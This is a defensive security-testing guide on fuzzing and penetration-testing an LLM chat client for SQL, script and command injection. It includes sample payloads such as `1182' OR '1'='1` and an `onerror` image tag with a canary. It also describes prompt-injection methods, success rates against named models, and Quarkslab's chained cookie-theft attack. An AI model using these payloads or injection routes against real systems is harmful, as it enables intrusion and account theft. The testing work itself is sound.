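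Testing the staff terminal tool requires a terminal emulator, a library that keeps the screen in memory as a grid of characters and colours. The test fills part of the screen with known text, saves the state, feeds in the tool's output and compares the new state with the saved one. The earlier text should be unchanged, and the new text should have only the tool's own colours. An emulator may ignore sequences that a real terminal acts on, such as clipboard writes, so the test should also check the raw output for control characters that are absent when the reply is harmless. It can catch fake tickets by comparing the number of tickets on the screen with the number in the database.

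For the database, the oracle reads the query log, replaces every value with a question mark and compares the result with an ordinary lookup:

```sql
-- order_id is 1182
SELECT status FROM orders WHERE id = ?

-- order_id is 1182' OR '1'='1
SELECT status FROM orders WHERE id = ? OR ? = ?
```

The query's structure has changed, so part of the order number became SQL. *Mutation Analysis* (2022) calls oracles metamorphic if they rely on a relation between inputs. Here the relation is that changing the order number must never change the query's structure.

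Order 1183 passes this check because a query for someone else's order has the same structure as a query for the customer's own. The tester can catch the leak by putting a unique canary in each test customer's delivery address, then searching for that canary in other customers' pages and in the client's requests to the stub. This also works when the model writes the whole query and its structure varies. Comparing the tables before and after each reply shows whether a read-only tool changed any data.

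Shell, file and evaluation calls need hooks, small functions that run whenever the client makes such a call. Python has a built-in mechanism for this:

```python
import sys

WATCHED = {"os.system", "subprocess.Popen", "compile", "open", "pickle.find_class"}
events = []

def watch(event, args):
    if event in WATCHED:
        events.append((event, repr(args)))

sys.addaudithook(watch)
```

After each reply, the test searches `events` for the marker. File paths need more care because many paths can lead to the same file. Ananto and colleagues' fuzzer resolves every `..` and symbolic link before it compares the path with the permitted folder. A Python hook can't observe what another program does after the client starts it, so the test should also look for new files afterwards.

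The last event in the list, `pickle.find_class`, occurs when Python's own deserializer looks up a class, before it creates the object. For other formats, the oracle can inspect the restored data and report any type that isn't on a short allowlist. This check would have missed the LangChain flaw, where the restored value was an ordinary string, `fake-secret`. The test should therefore also check that data comes back unchanged (`loads(dumps(data)) == data`).

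### What existing injection detectors check

Some fuzzers already include detectors for injection. JUG Switzerland's *Fuzzing Java with Jazzer* (2022), a talk about an open-source Java fuzzer, argues that because fuzzers already explore programs well, they only need to detect vulnerabilities when they occur. Many of the detectors use a marker, a particular string that the fuzzer tries to get into a dangerous function. A hook on that function reports when the string arrives.

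The table is based on 2023 source code for Jazzer from its developer, Code Intelligence, and on documentation for two JavaScript fuzzers, Jazzer.js and Vitiate. The Vitiate entries come from its *Detectors Reference*.

| Detector | Reports a bug when |
|---|---|
| Jazzer, commands | The client starts a program named `jazze` |
| Jazzer, SQL | A query is invalid SQL and the database returns an error |
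| Jazzer, script engines | The evaluated text contains `"jaz"+"zer"` |
| Jazzer, deserialization | The client loads `jaz.Zer`, a class that exists only as bait |
| Jazzer, network | The client tries to connect to a host the tester has not permitted |
| Jazzer.js, code | Code reads or calls a planted canary |
| Vitiate, commands | `vitiate_cmd_inject` appears in a command or its arguments |
| Vitiate, files | The client opens a forbidden path |

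Of the two command detectors, Jazzer can miss an injection and Vitiate can report a safe call. Jazzer compares only the program's name. If a client passes `aws -h;jazze` to a shell, the program the client starts is the shell, so Jazzer reports nothing. Vitiate also searches the arguments and would catch this. But it would also report a client that uses the recommended fix, which is to pass the marker as one item in a list of arguments without a shell. The shop can avoid both errors by using a command that creates a marker file and checking whether the file exists.

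Jazzer's SQL detector reports an injection only when the resulting query is invalid. It would miss a successful attack such as `1182' OR '1'='1`, which leaves the query valid, but the grammar's lone quotation mark would break the query and expose the flaw. A payload list used with this detector should therefore include broken SQL as well as working attacks. Code Intelligence expects some false alarms because the detector's parser does not support every database's dialect.

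Default settings are also worth checking. Vitiate's guide, *Vulnerability Detectors*, describes a default that blocks file access outside the project folder, but the more detailed reference describes a much weaker one that reports only access to `/etc/passwd` (or a similar file on Windows). With that weaker default, the fuzzer would miss access to the shop's `../canary-a17`. Jazzer's network detector is strict by default, and Code Intelligence's *Class BugDetectors* explains how to permit particular hosts. The shop would have to permit the stub and the scratch database, or every test would fail.

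### When an exception is a bug

None of these checks shows whether an exception indicates a bug. *LogicHunter* (Long, Zhao and Wang, 2026) studied this problem in LangChain, LlamaIndex and CrewAI, three Python frameworks for building agents. Faults in Python code rarely crash the interpreter. They raise exceptions such as `ValueError`, but so does correct code when a caller gives it a bad argument. The researchers labelled 1,000 distinct failures from their generated tests and found only 28 bugs. Many other bugs raise no exception.

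The fuzzer LogicHunter has a language model write tests based on each framework's source code, documentation and use in real projects. The tests include probes, which are assertions about what should happen. One test inserted the same fact twice into LlamaIndex's graph store, and its probe checked for a single copy, but there were two. LogicHunter then discards duplicate failures and failures that the test script itself caused.

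An agentic oracle investigates the rest. It is a language model that can look up source code, search the documentation and run code in a sandbox. It must investigate for several rounds before giving a verdict, and LogicHunter reports a bug only if four separate sessions agree. For the graph store, the oracle found that the code saved each fact as a list but looked for duplicates as tuples. A Python list never equals a tuple, so the search never found a match.

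LogicHunter found 40 previously unknown bugs, 32 of which were silent. Developers confirmed 30 and fixed 26. Four other test generators reported none, but that comparison alone would be unfair because two of them count only hard crashes and the other two aim to raise code coverage. Long and colleagues therefore ran the four generators' 506 usable failures through the agentic oracle and checked them by hand. This revealed one genuine bug, which LogicHunter had also found, so the other tools' tests were weak as well as their oracles.

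On the 1,000 labelled failures, the oracles compared as follows:

| Oracle | Reports that were real bugs | Real bugs it reported |
|---|---|---|
| Every failure counts as a bug | 2.8% | 100% |
| Filter based on the stack trace | 5.8% | 100% |
| GPT-5.2, shown the test and the error | 29.3% | 59.3% |
| GPT-5.2, also shown the documentation | 29.0% | 65.7% |
| Agentic oracle, using the smaller GPT-5-mini | 91.2% | 72.1% |

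In the last row, the oracle recognised about 20 of the 28 bugs and raised two false alarms. It did less well on 31 bugs that developers had already found and fixed, recognising 61%. Judges without tools recognised between 68% and 95% of those bugs but raised many more false alarms. Long and colleagues explain that their oracle requires stronger evidence, which is hard to get when a bug involves an outside service or several steps.

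The paper lists other limits. LogicHunter needs good examples of how people use an API, and it is poorly suited to bugs that involve several APIs or the contents of a database. The oracle is slow, and its verdicts can vary between runs. The evaluation covers only three Python frameworks, one model for writing tests and another for judging them.

Those limits exclude much of what the shop has to test, and LogicHunter looks for general logic errors rather than injection. It would be most useful for sorting exceptions when no marker has appeared anywhere. If a marker has appeared, the shop doesn't need a model to judge the response. Ananto and colleagues also don't use a model to decide the verdict. They use it only to choose which checks suit a tool and to write the first inputs.

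### False alarms

Searching the page's source for dangerous words creates false alarms. If the client escapes the image tag with the error handler, the customer sees the code as text, but `onerror` is still in the source. The browser oracle avoids this because it checks whether the script runs.

Ananto and colleagues' fuzzer reported 508 candidates. The researchers checked them by hand, rejecting 103 as harmless and removing 152 duplicates, leaving 253 confirmed bugs. In 115 of these, a tool returns hostile text without escaping it. Whether this does harm depends on the program that displays the text. A tester at the shop would have to trace the text to the chat page or the terminal before calling the bug a vulnerability.

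Tools that are meant to run code cause another kind of false alarm. One server in the study lets a model run AppleScript, the Mac's scripting language. A competing tool, VIPER-MCP, sent it a command to print a system file and counted the result as an exploit, even though the AppleScript tool is meant to run commands. Ananto and colleagues handle this by having a model read each tool's description and decide whether the tool must reject a suspicious input, may return only a safe value such as an empty list, or may accept the input. Their fuzzer called the AppleScript tool more than 2,000 times without raising an alarm. For such a tool, the shop should test whether the code can get out of its sandbox.

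Choosing checks in this way misses some real bugs. When the researchers turned on all 74 checks for every tool, they found 13 bugs that the normal setting had missed. Five were in a single WordPress server written in JavaScript, for which the model had chosen a check that works only in Python. But turning on every check also more than doubled the number of reports, and on tools that only this setting flagged, over 90% of the reports were false.

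Jazzer.js lets testers silence a known false alarm by matching part of its stack trace, the list of function calls that led to it. The pattern should be as narrow as possible, because one that matches a whole file will also silence any real bugs in that file.

### Missed harm and planted bugs

An oracle that checks only the page that received the reply will miss delayed effects. Suppose the customer's page escapes a hostile ticket summary correctly, but the client also stores the summary. A week later, a support worker opens the ticket on an internal page that doesn't escape HTML, and the script in the summary runs in the worker's session. Ananto and colleagues' fuzzer would not test for this because it calls one tool at a time. They leave sequences of calls to future work.

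The shop needs a second pass after each batch of hostile replies. The test logs in as a different customer and then as a support worker, opens every page that shows stored text, and runs the staff terminal tool. It should also trigger scheduled jobs, such as a nightly e-mail, immediately. The canary server should keep running after the tests end, with a record of which address belonged to which reply.

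To learn how much the oracles still miss, the tester can plant bugs in a copy of the client and count how many the tests find:

| Planted bug | What should notice it |
|---|---|
| The chat page skips its sanitizer | The headless browser |
| The client pastes the order number into its SQL | The comparison of query structures |
| `find_order` ignores who is logged in | The canary in another customer's address |
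| The terminal tool prints summaries unchanged | The terminal comparison |
| An internal page shows stored tickets without escaping them | The second pass, as a support worker |
| The client uses a LangChain version with the `lc` flaw | The check that data comes back unchanged |

When the tests miss a planted bug, the next step is to find out whether the hostile text reached the faulty code. Fleischer, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Contextualizing Sink Knowledge for Java Vulnerability Discovery*, made this distinction in running Jazzer on programs with 54 known vulnerabilities. They gave each test program 50 processor cores for 24 hours. Jazzer never reached the vulnerable code in 25 cases, reached it without triggering a detector in 21, and reported the vulnerability in 8.

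Of those 21 failures, 18 occurred because the exploit needed input that random changes rarely produce, such as XML that satisfied a set of type rules. In one case, Jazzer had no hook on the relevant function to guide it towards an exploit. If the shop's hostile text never reaches the planted bug, the tester should work on the generator or the stub. If the text reaches the bug and nothing happens, the payload may be wrong for that sink, or the oracle may be checking the wrong place.

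Even if the tests find all six planted bugs, their true miss rate p could be as high as 39%. This figure comes from solving (1 - p)^6 = 0.05, the calculation behind the stopping rule for random replies. It assumes the planted bugs resemble the real ones, but testers tend to plant bugs they have already thought of. Including real vulnerabilities from old library versions, like the LangChain flaw in the table, helps to correct this bias.

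### One failing reply, from alarm to regression test

Suppose the browser oracle reports that script ran on the shop's chat page, and the stub's log records seed 4471, turn 2. The tester first restarts the stub with that seed and the same version of `REPLIES`, resets the client and repeats the conversation. If the failure does not return, it may depend on something left over from earlier conversations, so the tester replays those from the log too. Jazzer does some of this for Java programs. According to Code Intelligence, it prints the exception with the input that caused it, and can produce a small program that reproduces the failure.

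Next comes shrinking, which means removing parts of the reply for as long as it still fails. A program can do this automatically, because the oracle decides after each attempt:

```text
start:  > **<img src='/missing-a17.png' onerror="document.title='canary-a17'">**
        (blank line) Anything else?

remove "Anything else?"         still fails, so leave it out
remove "> "                     passes, so put it back
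remove both "**"                still fails, so leave them out
shorten the image's address     still fails, so keep the short one

end:    > <img src=x onerror="document.title='canary-a17'">
```

The `>` at the start of a line is Markdown for a quotation. The same image in a plain sentence does no harm, so the developer knows to check how the client renders quotations. The renderer handles them in a separate function that doesn't escape HTML.

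One bug usually produces several alarms. The shop's grammar puts this image inside a quotation in 8 of its 144 pages, so the test run may report the same fault eight times. LogicHunter groups exceptions by the file, function and line where they occurred. That works less well here, because every reply that runs script enters the chat page through the same line of code. Grouping alarms by the shrunken text is more informative. The grammar's `javascript:` link, for example, would shrink to a different text and probably needs a separate fix.

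Sanitizing the finished HTML once, after converting all the Markdown, is safer than adding the missing escape to the quotation function, because the next new function might have the same gap. After the fix, the tester reruns every reply that failed in the original run. Those that now pass had failed because of this bug, and the rest need separate investigation. The fix is more urgent if the manual tests show that an attacker could get the real model to send such a reply.

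The shrunken reply becomes a permanent test. In simplified form, it might look like this:

```python
def test_html_in_quotation(stub, chat):
    stub.reply("> canary-a17")
    assert "canary-a17" in chat.ask("Where is order 1182?")

    stub.reply("> <img src=x onerror=\"document.title='canary-a17'\">")
    chat.ask("Where is order 1182?")
    assert chat.title_after(seconds=2) != "canary-a17"
```

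The first half is a control that confirms that the page received the stub's reply and that the fix did not remove ordinary quotations. The test stores the text rather than seed 4471 because any change to `REPLIES` could make that seed select a different reply. Before relying on the test, the developer should run it once against the old code to confirm that it fails.

The test then runs in the build pipeline, the automatic checks on every code change, and a failure blocks the release. The pipeline has to run the oracle too, because without it the old bug could return and the client would still finish normally. Vitiate's detectors work both during fuzzing and in its regression mode for saved inputs. The shop's pipeline also needs the headless browser and enough time for the image to fail.

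## Manual penetration tests and checks against the real model

The stub made the shop's chat page run script by putting an image inside a quotation. The developer may object that a real model would never send such a reply. The same objection applies to almost every finding from a stub, because the tester wrote the reply.

An attacker who controls the model server or a router can write the reply directly, as the stub does. Other attackers have to get the model to write it, and models often comply. In *Make Agent Defeat Agent*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2025) found 34 vulnerabilities in open-source agents by sending a live model prompts that contained harmless test code. They then replaced the test code with real attacks, and all 34 still worked. Only 14 required prompt injection tricks to get past the model's instructions or safety training. Strange replies may not be hard to get either,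 since many models can write terminal control characters.

But the objection is right about priorities. A bug that any customer can trigger with one message is more urgent than one that requires a compromised router, even if both are in the same line of code. Roseberry's "assume jailbreak" helps a tester choose which replies to send, but not rank the resulting findings, because it treats every reply as obtainable. How easily an attacker can trigger a bug should therefore help determine its severity and how soon it is fixed. Difficulty of triggering is a poor reason to leave a bug unfixed, since the provider may replace the model with one that is easier to manipulate.

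### How often current models follow injected instructions

Model developers publish injection results in system cards, the reports that accompany new models. VentureBeat covers the results for Claude Opus 4.6 (February 2026), and The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* covers those for Claude Opus 5 (July 2026). TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) covers results that OpenAI added in August.

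| Model | Setting | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Restricted coding environment | None in 200 attempts |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, no safeguards | 17.8% at one attempt, 78.6% by the 200th |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, with safeguards | 57.1% by the 200th attempt |
| Claude Opus 5 | Web browser | None in 129 scenarios |
| Claude Opus 5 | General test by the security firm Gray Swan | 2.0% after 15 attempts |
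| GPT-5.6 Sol | Direct injection in chat | About 0.05% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Indirect injection through outside content | 3.77% on average |

Models are getting harder to hijack. On the Gray Swan test, attacks succeeded against the earlier Opus 4.8 in 5.5% of cases. But the tests use different attacks and different numbers of attempts, so the table can't be used to rank the models. The results for Opus 4.6 also show that the success rate depends heavily on the product around the model, so the shop can't assume that a figure from a system card applies to its own assistant.

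Repeated attempts help an attacker, though less than simple probability suggests. If every attempt on Opus 4.6 had an independent 17.8% chance, the total would have passed 78.6% by the eighth attempt:

```text
1 - (1 - 0.178)^8 ≈ 79%
```

Instead, it was still 78.6% at the 200th. Some attacks probably work quickly while others almost never do.

Even a low success rate can be enough for an attacker who plants text and waits. For example, if a hostile product review succeeds 3.77% of the times the model reads it, and 1,000 customers ask about that product, the model follows the review's instructions in about 38 conversations.

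Independent tests are usually smaller. In *The Prompt Injection Quest to RCE with Fable-5 in Claude Code*, veganmosfet (2026) asked Claude Fable 5 to summarise a code repository that contained only a simple README. Injected instructions could lead the agent to run untrusted code without asking. In two of the ten runs, the agent inspected the code closely and refused. In four, the attack triggered Anthropic's safety classifiers, which are separate filters for dangerous content. Ten runs are too few for a reliable rate, but they show that an ordinary request can still lead the agent to run untrusted code.

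Filters can also change which model answers. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Fable 5.1 describes extra safeguards in areas such as biology and cybersecurity. paddo (2026), in *The Cage Is in the Table Now*, reports that these safeguards can hand a task to a fallback model, and that every successful attack in Anthropic's tests ran on the fallback. A review of the same card, *Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1*, says that resistance to indirect injection has improved. The improvement may not extend to the fallback, so a shop that chose Fable for its resistance should also test the fallback.

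Anthropic replaced Fable 5.1 in November. *Fable and Mythos 5.2* (Mowshowitz, 2026) lists a new section on prompt injection in the successor's system card. Testers should look up the card for the exact model they use and check again after every update.

### Fuzzers that keep the model in the loop

Four research tools automate the search for input that makes a live model trigger a bug. The one that Liu and colleagues built is AgentFuzz, which works backwards from the sink:

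1. It searches the agent's source code for dangerous functions and traces the calls that lead to each one.
2. A language model reads the names of the functions and classes along the way, then writes a request that should make the agent use them.
3. AgentFuzz sends the request and scores the result. A request scores well if it suits the tool's purpose and the program gets close to the sink.
4. If the agent chose the wrong tool, the language model rewords the request. If a condition in the code stopped the value, a constraint solver calculates one that would pass.
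5. A hook on the sink reports when a harmless payload, such as `print(1)`, arrives.

In one agent, a search tool evaluated whatever followed the label `source_doc:`. AgentFuzz found that the request had to contain this label, which random changes would have been very unlikely to produce.

The researchers ran AgentFuzz on 828 calls to dangerous functions, with a limit of five minutes for each. Token costs averaged at most $6.90 per agent. The researchers checked all 34 reports by hand and found them correct. LLMSmith, an older static analysis tool, found 10 of the same bugs and raised 332 false alarms.

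To estimate what AgentFuzz had missed, the researchers picked 83 of the other 794 calls at random and read the code. They found one vulnerable call, in the agent Devika, where the payload was stored first and reached the sink only during a second exchange in the same chat. One miss in about a tenth of the calls suggests around ten among all 794, although a single case is weak evidence. The paper's recall of 97% counts only the one miss, so it is probably too high.

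ChainFuzzer, Wu and colleagues' tool for testing sequences of tool calls, has to make the model follow a whole sequence. It compares the agent's actual calls with the intended ones, then uses a second model to repair the request where they differ. It accepts a request only after five successful runs in a row. Disguising the payloads raised the share that took effect to 89%. Testing an agent took an average of 3.4 hours and about 6 million tokens.

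Wu and colleagues don't give a false-positive rate for their 365 vulnerabilities. For the 121 command injections, ChainFuzzer required only that the attacker's text reach a function that runs commands, and some of those functions may exist to run whatever the user requests. The payload came from the user in 225 cases, and whether that is a security breach depends on whose computer the agent runs on. The other 140 payloads came through outside content, such as web pages, and those cases are easier to count as attacks.

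*Can Agents Trust Their Skills?* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) studies skills, which are packages of instructions, code and other files that users install to teach an agent a task. The researchers' fuzzer, TrustProbe, writes a plausible skill containing a canary, installs it and starts a fresh session. It confirms an attacker's control when the canary reaches a dangerous function by the expected route. The researchers count a vulnerability only if they also see the harm, such as a new file or a request to their test server.

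This evidence is stronger than ChainFuzzer's, but TrustProbe's perfect score in a comparison with two rival tools means little because the researchers used TrustProbe's own verified findings as the list of correct answers. The main test also used permissive settings. Under the strictest settings that still allowed unattended runs, 31 of the 89 vulnerabilities that the researchers could retest remained exploitable.

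They also tested 633 real skills, in 2,963 combinations of skill and agent. In about a quarter of the runs, text from the skill travelled along one of the vulnerable paths. This doesn't mean the skills were malicious, but small edits turned 15 of them into complete attacks.

*Autonomy Comes with Costs*, by Luo, Dai and colleagues, presents AgentDoS, which looks for requests that exhaust an agent's resources. It analyses how the agent manages those resources, then uses a language model to write requests that increase consumption. A stub can send an endless reply, but AgentDoS tests whether an ordinary-looking request can make a live agent do excessive work.

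| Tool | What it looks for | Agents tested | New vulnerabilities | False positives |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentFuzz | One prompt that reaches a dangerous function | 20 | 34 in 14 agents, with 23 CVE identifiers | None |
| ChainFuzzer | Harmful sequences of tool calls | 20 | 365 in 19 agents | No rate given |
| TrustProbe | Harm caused by installed skills | 11 | 104 in 11 agents | None after checking for harm |
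| AgentDoS | Exhausted resources | 20 | 36 in 16 agents, with 15 CVE identifiers | No rate in the abstract |

### What a live model adds and what it costs

A stub test covers only what happens after the model responds. These fuzzers also test which tool the model calls, how it rewrites the attacker's text, and whether the developer's instructions or the model's training stops the attack.

They can also show that an attack's success depends on how the text reaches the model. Wang and colleagues pasted the text of the skills behind their 104 vulnerabilities into ordinary chat messages, and only 33 of the attacks still worked. In the agent OpenClaw, the number fell from 24 to one. OpenClaw lists the installed skills and tells the model to read and follow the matching one, so text in a skill has an authority that the same text in a chat message lacks. A tester who used only the chat box would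 have missed most of these attacks.

The drawback is that every result depends on a particular model. AgentFuzz's targets ran on GPT-4o, ChainFuzzer's on GPT-5.1 and TrustProbe's on deepseek-v4-flash. Using one model throughout makes it easier to compare the agents in a study, but does not show how many of the attacks would work on a more resistant model.

A clean run is even harder to interpret. Wang and colleagues ran AgentFuzz on four Python agents in which TrustProbe had found 20 vulnerabilities. AgentFuzz made about 2,425 attempts over 57 hours and found none, because its prompts didn't lead the model along the routes that an installed skill would have opened.

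ChainFuzzer's results also depended heavily on persuading the model. Without its prompt repairs it found 96 vulnerabilities instead of 365, and without disguised payloads it found 132. A model that was harder to persuade would have lowered the count in a similar way, but the faulty code would still have been there. That is a good reason to look for client bugs with a stub first, then use a live model to find out who can trigger them.

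The shop has only four sinks, so it can answer that question by hand. A team with hundreds of tools would save time with a fuzzer.

### The manual procedure

The tester needs written permission from the shop, a copy of the system with invented customers, and a spending limit for model calls. Payloads remain harmless markers. For each bug, and for each sink where the stub found nothing, the tester then works through six steps:

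1. Read the code around the sink. Start at the function that acts on the reply and trace the text backwards, noting every check on the way. Look for checks that exist only in a prompt, and for other routes to the same function.
2. Edit a live reply through the proxy. Ask the assistant an ordinary question and put the marker into the real answer before it reaches the client. If the bug appears, it does not depend on a mistake in the stub's format. This also demonstrates what a hostile router could do.
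3. Try direct prompt injection. Acting as a customer, ask the model for the reply that broke the client. Begin with a plain request, such as asking it to quote a line of HTML. If that works, an attacker needs no tricks.
4. Try indirect prompt injection. Put the instruction where an outsider could put it, such as a product review or a supplier's e-mail. Then log in as a different test customer and ask an ordinary question about the product.
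5. Combine the bug with ordinary web flaws. Find out who else can open the conversation, what a script on the page could do, and where else the client shows the stored text.
6. Repeat the attempts in fresh conversations and record every success and failure.

Reading the code often explains why a safeguard fails. Wang and colleagues found approval rules that some parts of a program never applied, and others that didn't cover the dangerous operation. Liu and colleagues noticed that agent developers often instruct the model to refuse dangerous requests even where a check in the code would work. In Microsoft's TaskWeaver, for instance, the prompt instructed the planning model to reject anything with potential security risks. A tester should find out what the code does if the model doesn't follow such an instruction.

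Step 4 is worth doing even if step 3 fails. The model may be more likely to follow instructions in a supplier's e-mail than in a customer's message, or the client may put the two in different parts of the request. The tester should first check the logged request to confirm that the review reached the model. If it didn't, the attempt tests the shop's search function but doesn't test the model's resistance.

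A normal-looking reply isn't reliable evidence that an attack failed either. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) report on a large public competition in indirect prompt injection, where an attack could succeed while the reply to the user looked normal. The shop's assistant might give the correct delivery date and also write a hostile ticket summary. The tester therefore needs to run the same oracles as in the stub tests, including the canary server and the query log.

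A test with a harmless marker can make an attack look easier than it is, because a model may repeat the marker but refuse a real exploit. Liu and colleagues eventually got every real attack through in their follow-up, which suggests that such refusals are a weak defence. The tester can report that the model delivered a marker of the same form as a real payload, and that the real payload might need more effort.

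### How many attempts to make

A single failure says very little. The tester should choose the number of attempts in advance, because stopping at the first success exaggerates the rate. If a fixed wording never succeeds, the calculation from the random stub tests gives the highest success rate that is still plausible:

| Attempts without a success | Highest plausible success rate (95% confidence) |
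|---|---|
| 10 | 26% |
| 20 | 14% |
| 50 | 6% |
| 100 | 3% |
| 300 | 1% |

Twenty failures are therefore compatible with an attack that works one time in eight. The table applies to one wording, one route and one model configuration. A better wording could succeed at once, so 20 failures with each of several good prompts are more informative than 300 with a clumsy one. The tester should report results for each wording separately, because an average could hide one that nearly always works.

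ChainFuzzer's rule of five successes in a row is useful when a developer needs a reliable demonstration, but it is the wrong standard for deciding whether a bug is reachable. A prompt that works half the time passes the rule only about 3% of the time (0.5^5), and one that works one time in 20 will almost never pass. But an attacker who can send the second prompt 59 times has a 95% chance of at least one success, if the attempts are independent.

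The number of attempts should reflect how many an attacker could make. A customer can send the shop's assistant hundreds of messages unless the shop limits the number. An attacker who can get only one e-mail past a supplier's staff has fewer chances, although the model may read that e-mail many times.

### How Quarkslab got from a chat reply to an administrator's account

The security company Quarkslab describes an authorised attack by its testers on a customer's live system, starting from an ordinary account. To protect the customer, the company rebuilt the flaws in a mock medical assistant called FailMed AI. The original model was no longer available, so the mock uses a model customised to reproduce the findings. It shows how the flaws combine, but can't be used to measure how often the customer's model complied.

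The testers began with Spikee, a tool that sends a prepared set of prompts to a model. The assistant had no effective limit on requests, so they could send a great many. While reading the results, they noticed that the model would repeat a Markdown image on request and that the page displayed it. Each weakness they found after that removed an obstacle left by the one before:

| Weakness | What it allowed | What still stood in the way |
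|---|---|---|
| The page loaded images from any address in a reply | An image address could carry medical data to an outside server | The victim had to send the attacker's prompt |
| The page displayed HTML from replies, and its CSP was inadequate | A reply could run script | It ran only in the attacker's own conversation |
| Script could read the session cookie | The script could copy a login | The only login within reach was the attacker's own |
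| The server didn't check who owned a conversation | Any logged-in user could open the attacker's conversation | The victim had to follow a link |

With all four, the attacker could save a hostile reply in their own conversation and send someone the link. When the victim opened it, the script sent the victim's session cookie to the attacker, who could then log in as the victim. This gave the attacker access to patients' records if the victim was a doctor, or control of the whole platform if the victim was an administrator.

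A stub would have exposed the image and script bugs quickly, but not the missing ownership check, which has nothing to do with the model. A tester who used only the visible features would also have missed it, because there was no button for sharing a conversation. Conversations had predictable addresses, and to find the flaw someone had to try opening one from another account.

The case also casts doubt on the low priority that the shop's threat model gave to customers who attack their own chat page. The script bug in the medical assistant seemed to harm only the attacker until the testers found a way to bring other people to the attacker's page. The low priority is justified only if no other customer, support worker or administrator can open the conversation in a page with the same bug.

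Quarkslab's main recommendation is to fix the sink by validating and encoding every reply, and then to add a strict CSP and ownership checks. This order makes sense because only fixing the sink removes the script. An ownership check would keep out other patients and doctors but would still have to admit an administrator who reviews flagged conversations. Hiding the cookie from scripts would prevent theft of the login, but a script on the administrator's page could still act with the administrator's rights.

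### What people find that generators miss

People no longer have a clear advantage over software in writing injections that work on models. OpenAI tested its automated attacker, GPT-Red, on indirect injection scenarios from Dziemian and colleagues. Against GPT-5.1, GPT-Red found a successful attack in 84% of the scenarios, compared with 13% for human testers. The shop can therefore leave much of the attack wording to software.

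Those scenarios came with a goal, however, whereas penetration testers have to work out which goals are worth pursuing and what counts as success. Spikee's prompts produced the image in the medical assistant, but Quarkslab's testers recognised it as a possible leak, kept looking for something worse and connected it to flaws elsewhere.

A person who knows the business can also recognise harm that leaves no technical trace. Suppose a ticket summary contains the words "refund approved". The text has no script, control character or canary, and it reaches the staff terminal tool as the developer intended. But if the shop's staff pay refunds based on the summary, a customer who can influence it can steal money. A generator can produce the text, but the tester has to ask the staff how they use the summaries.

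People are also better at following data over time. AgentFuzz missed the bug in Devika because the payload needed a second message. The second pass in the shop's stub tests opens only the pages its author knew about. A tester who works through a support worker's normal day may also find the marker in a weekly report or a spreadsheet export. The team can then add that route to the second pass.

A manual tester gets tired, tries familiar attacks first and can't test every boundary in a stream, so it makes sense to run the stub tests beforehand and keep the tester's time for access rules, unusual features and combinations of flaws.

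### Setting severity

A finding needs two ratings, one for how much harm it could do and one for how easily an attacker could cause it. The harm depends on the sink's privileges. The table gives a reasonable scale for reachability, with the strongest evidence at the top:

| Evidence | Example at the shop | When to repair it if the harm is serious |
|---|---|---|
| An outsider's text triggers the bug during normal use | A product review makes another customer's page run script | Before release |
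| An attacker triggers it directly and harms someone else | A customer gets the assistant to reveal another customer's order | Before release |
| It also needs a mistake or an unusual setting | A support worker has to open a link to the attacker's conversation | Before release if the mistake is easy to make, otherwise in the next version |
| It needs control of a server or router | A router changes a tool call | Before release if the shop uses outside routers, otherwise in the next version |
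| Only the stub has triggered it | No wording or route has worked so far | With the next change to that code |

This scale is a judgement, and the severity of the harm can change the order. A flaw that lets a hostile router run commands on the shop's server should come before one that lets any customer turn the text on their own screen red. A quick fix can also move a finding up, since adding the missing sanitizer takes less time than debating whether a model would ever write the payload.

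Because the two ratings are separate, the tester only needs to repeat the attempts and update the reachability rating when the provider changes the model. The harm stays the same. A new feature can also raise the reachability rating. If the shop adds a button for sharing conversations, a bug that could harm only the attacker may now affect everyone who receives a link.

Testers should be careful with the last row of the table, because "Only the stub has triggered it" may mean that an attack is difficult or that testers spent only a few minutes on it. The number of attempts distinguishes the two cases.

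### What the report should contain

The developer needs enough detail to reproduce the bug, and the manager needs enough to decide when to fix it. For the script in the quotation, the record might have these fields:

```text
Finding         HTML inside a Markdown quotation runs as script
Client          version, settings, and which safeguards were on
Stub reply      the shortened reply that triggers the bug
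Live reply      the complete reply from the real model, if it sent one
Route           product review -> request -> model -> chat page
Attacker needs  an account that can post reviews
Victim does     asks an ordinary question about the product
Model           name requested, name returned, settings, date, router
Attempts        successes and total for each wording and route
Evidence        oracle output, request log, canary server log
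Harm            what the script could do in the victim's session
Severity        harm and reachability, with the reason for each
Repair          sanitize the finished HTML; add a strict CSP
```

The log needs two entries for the model's name, the one the client requested and the one given in the reply, because a router or fallback may substitute a different model. The name in the reply can also be wrong, so the provider's usage records are useful if the shop can see them. Logs may contain working attacks or private text, so the tester should store them where the shop's ordinary staff tools won't display them.

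The report should also list what the tester left out, such as a mobile app, a language or a backup model. Otherwise, a reader may assume that the mobile app was tested and passed. The report should include the wording of failed attempts too, so that the next tester can repeat them on a new model.

After the repair, the tester reruns both the stub reply and the live attempts. Failed live attempts don't prove that the repair worked, because the model may have refused this time. The tester can mark the bug as fixed only once the stub reply reaches the page without triggering the injection.
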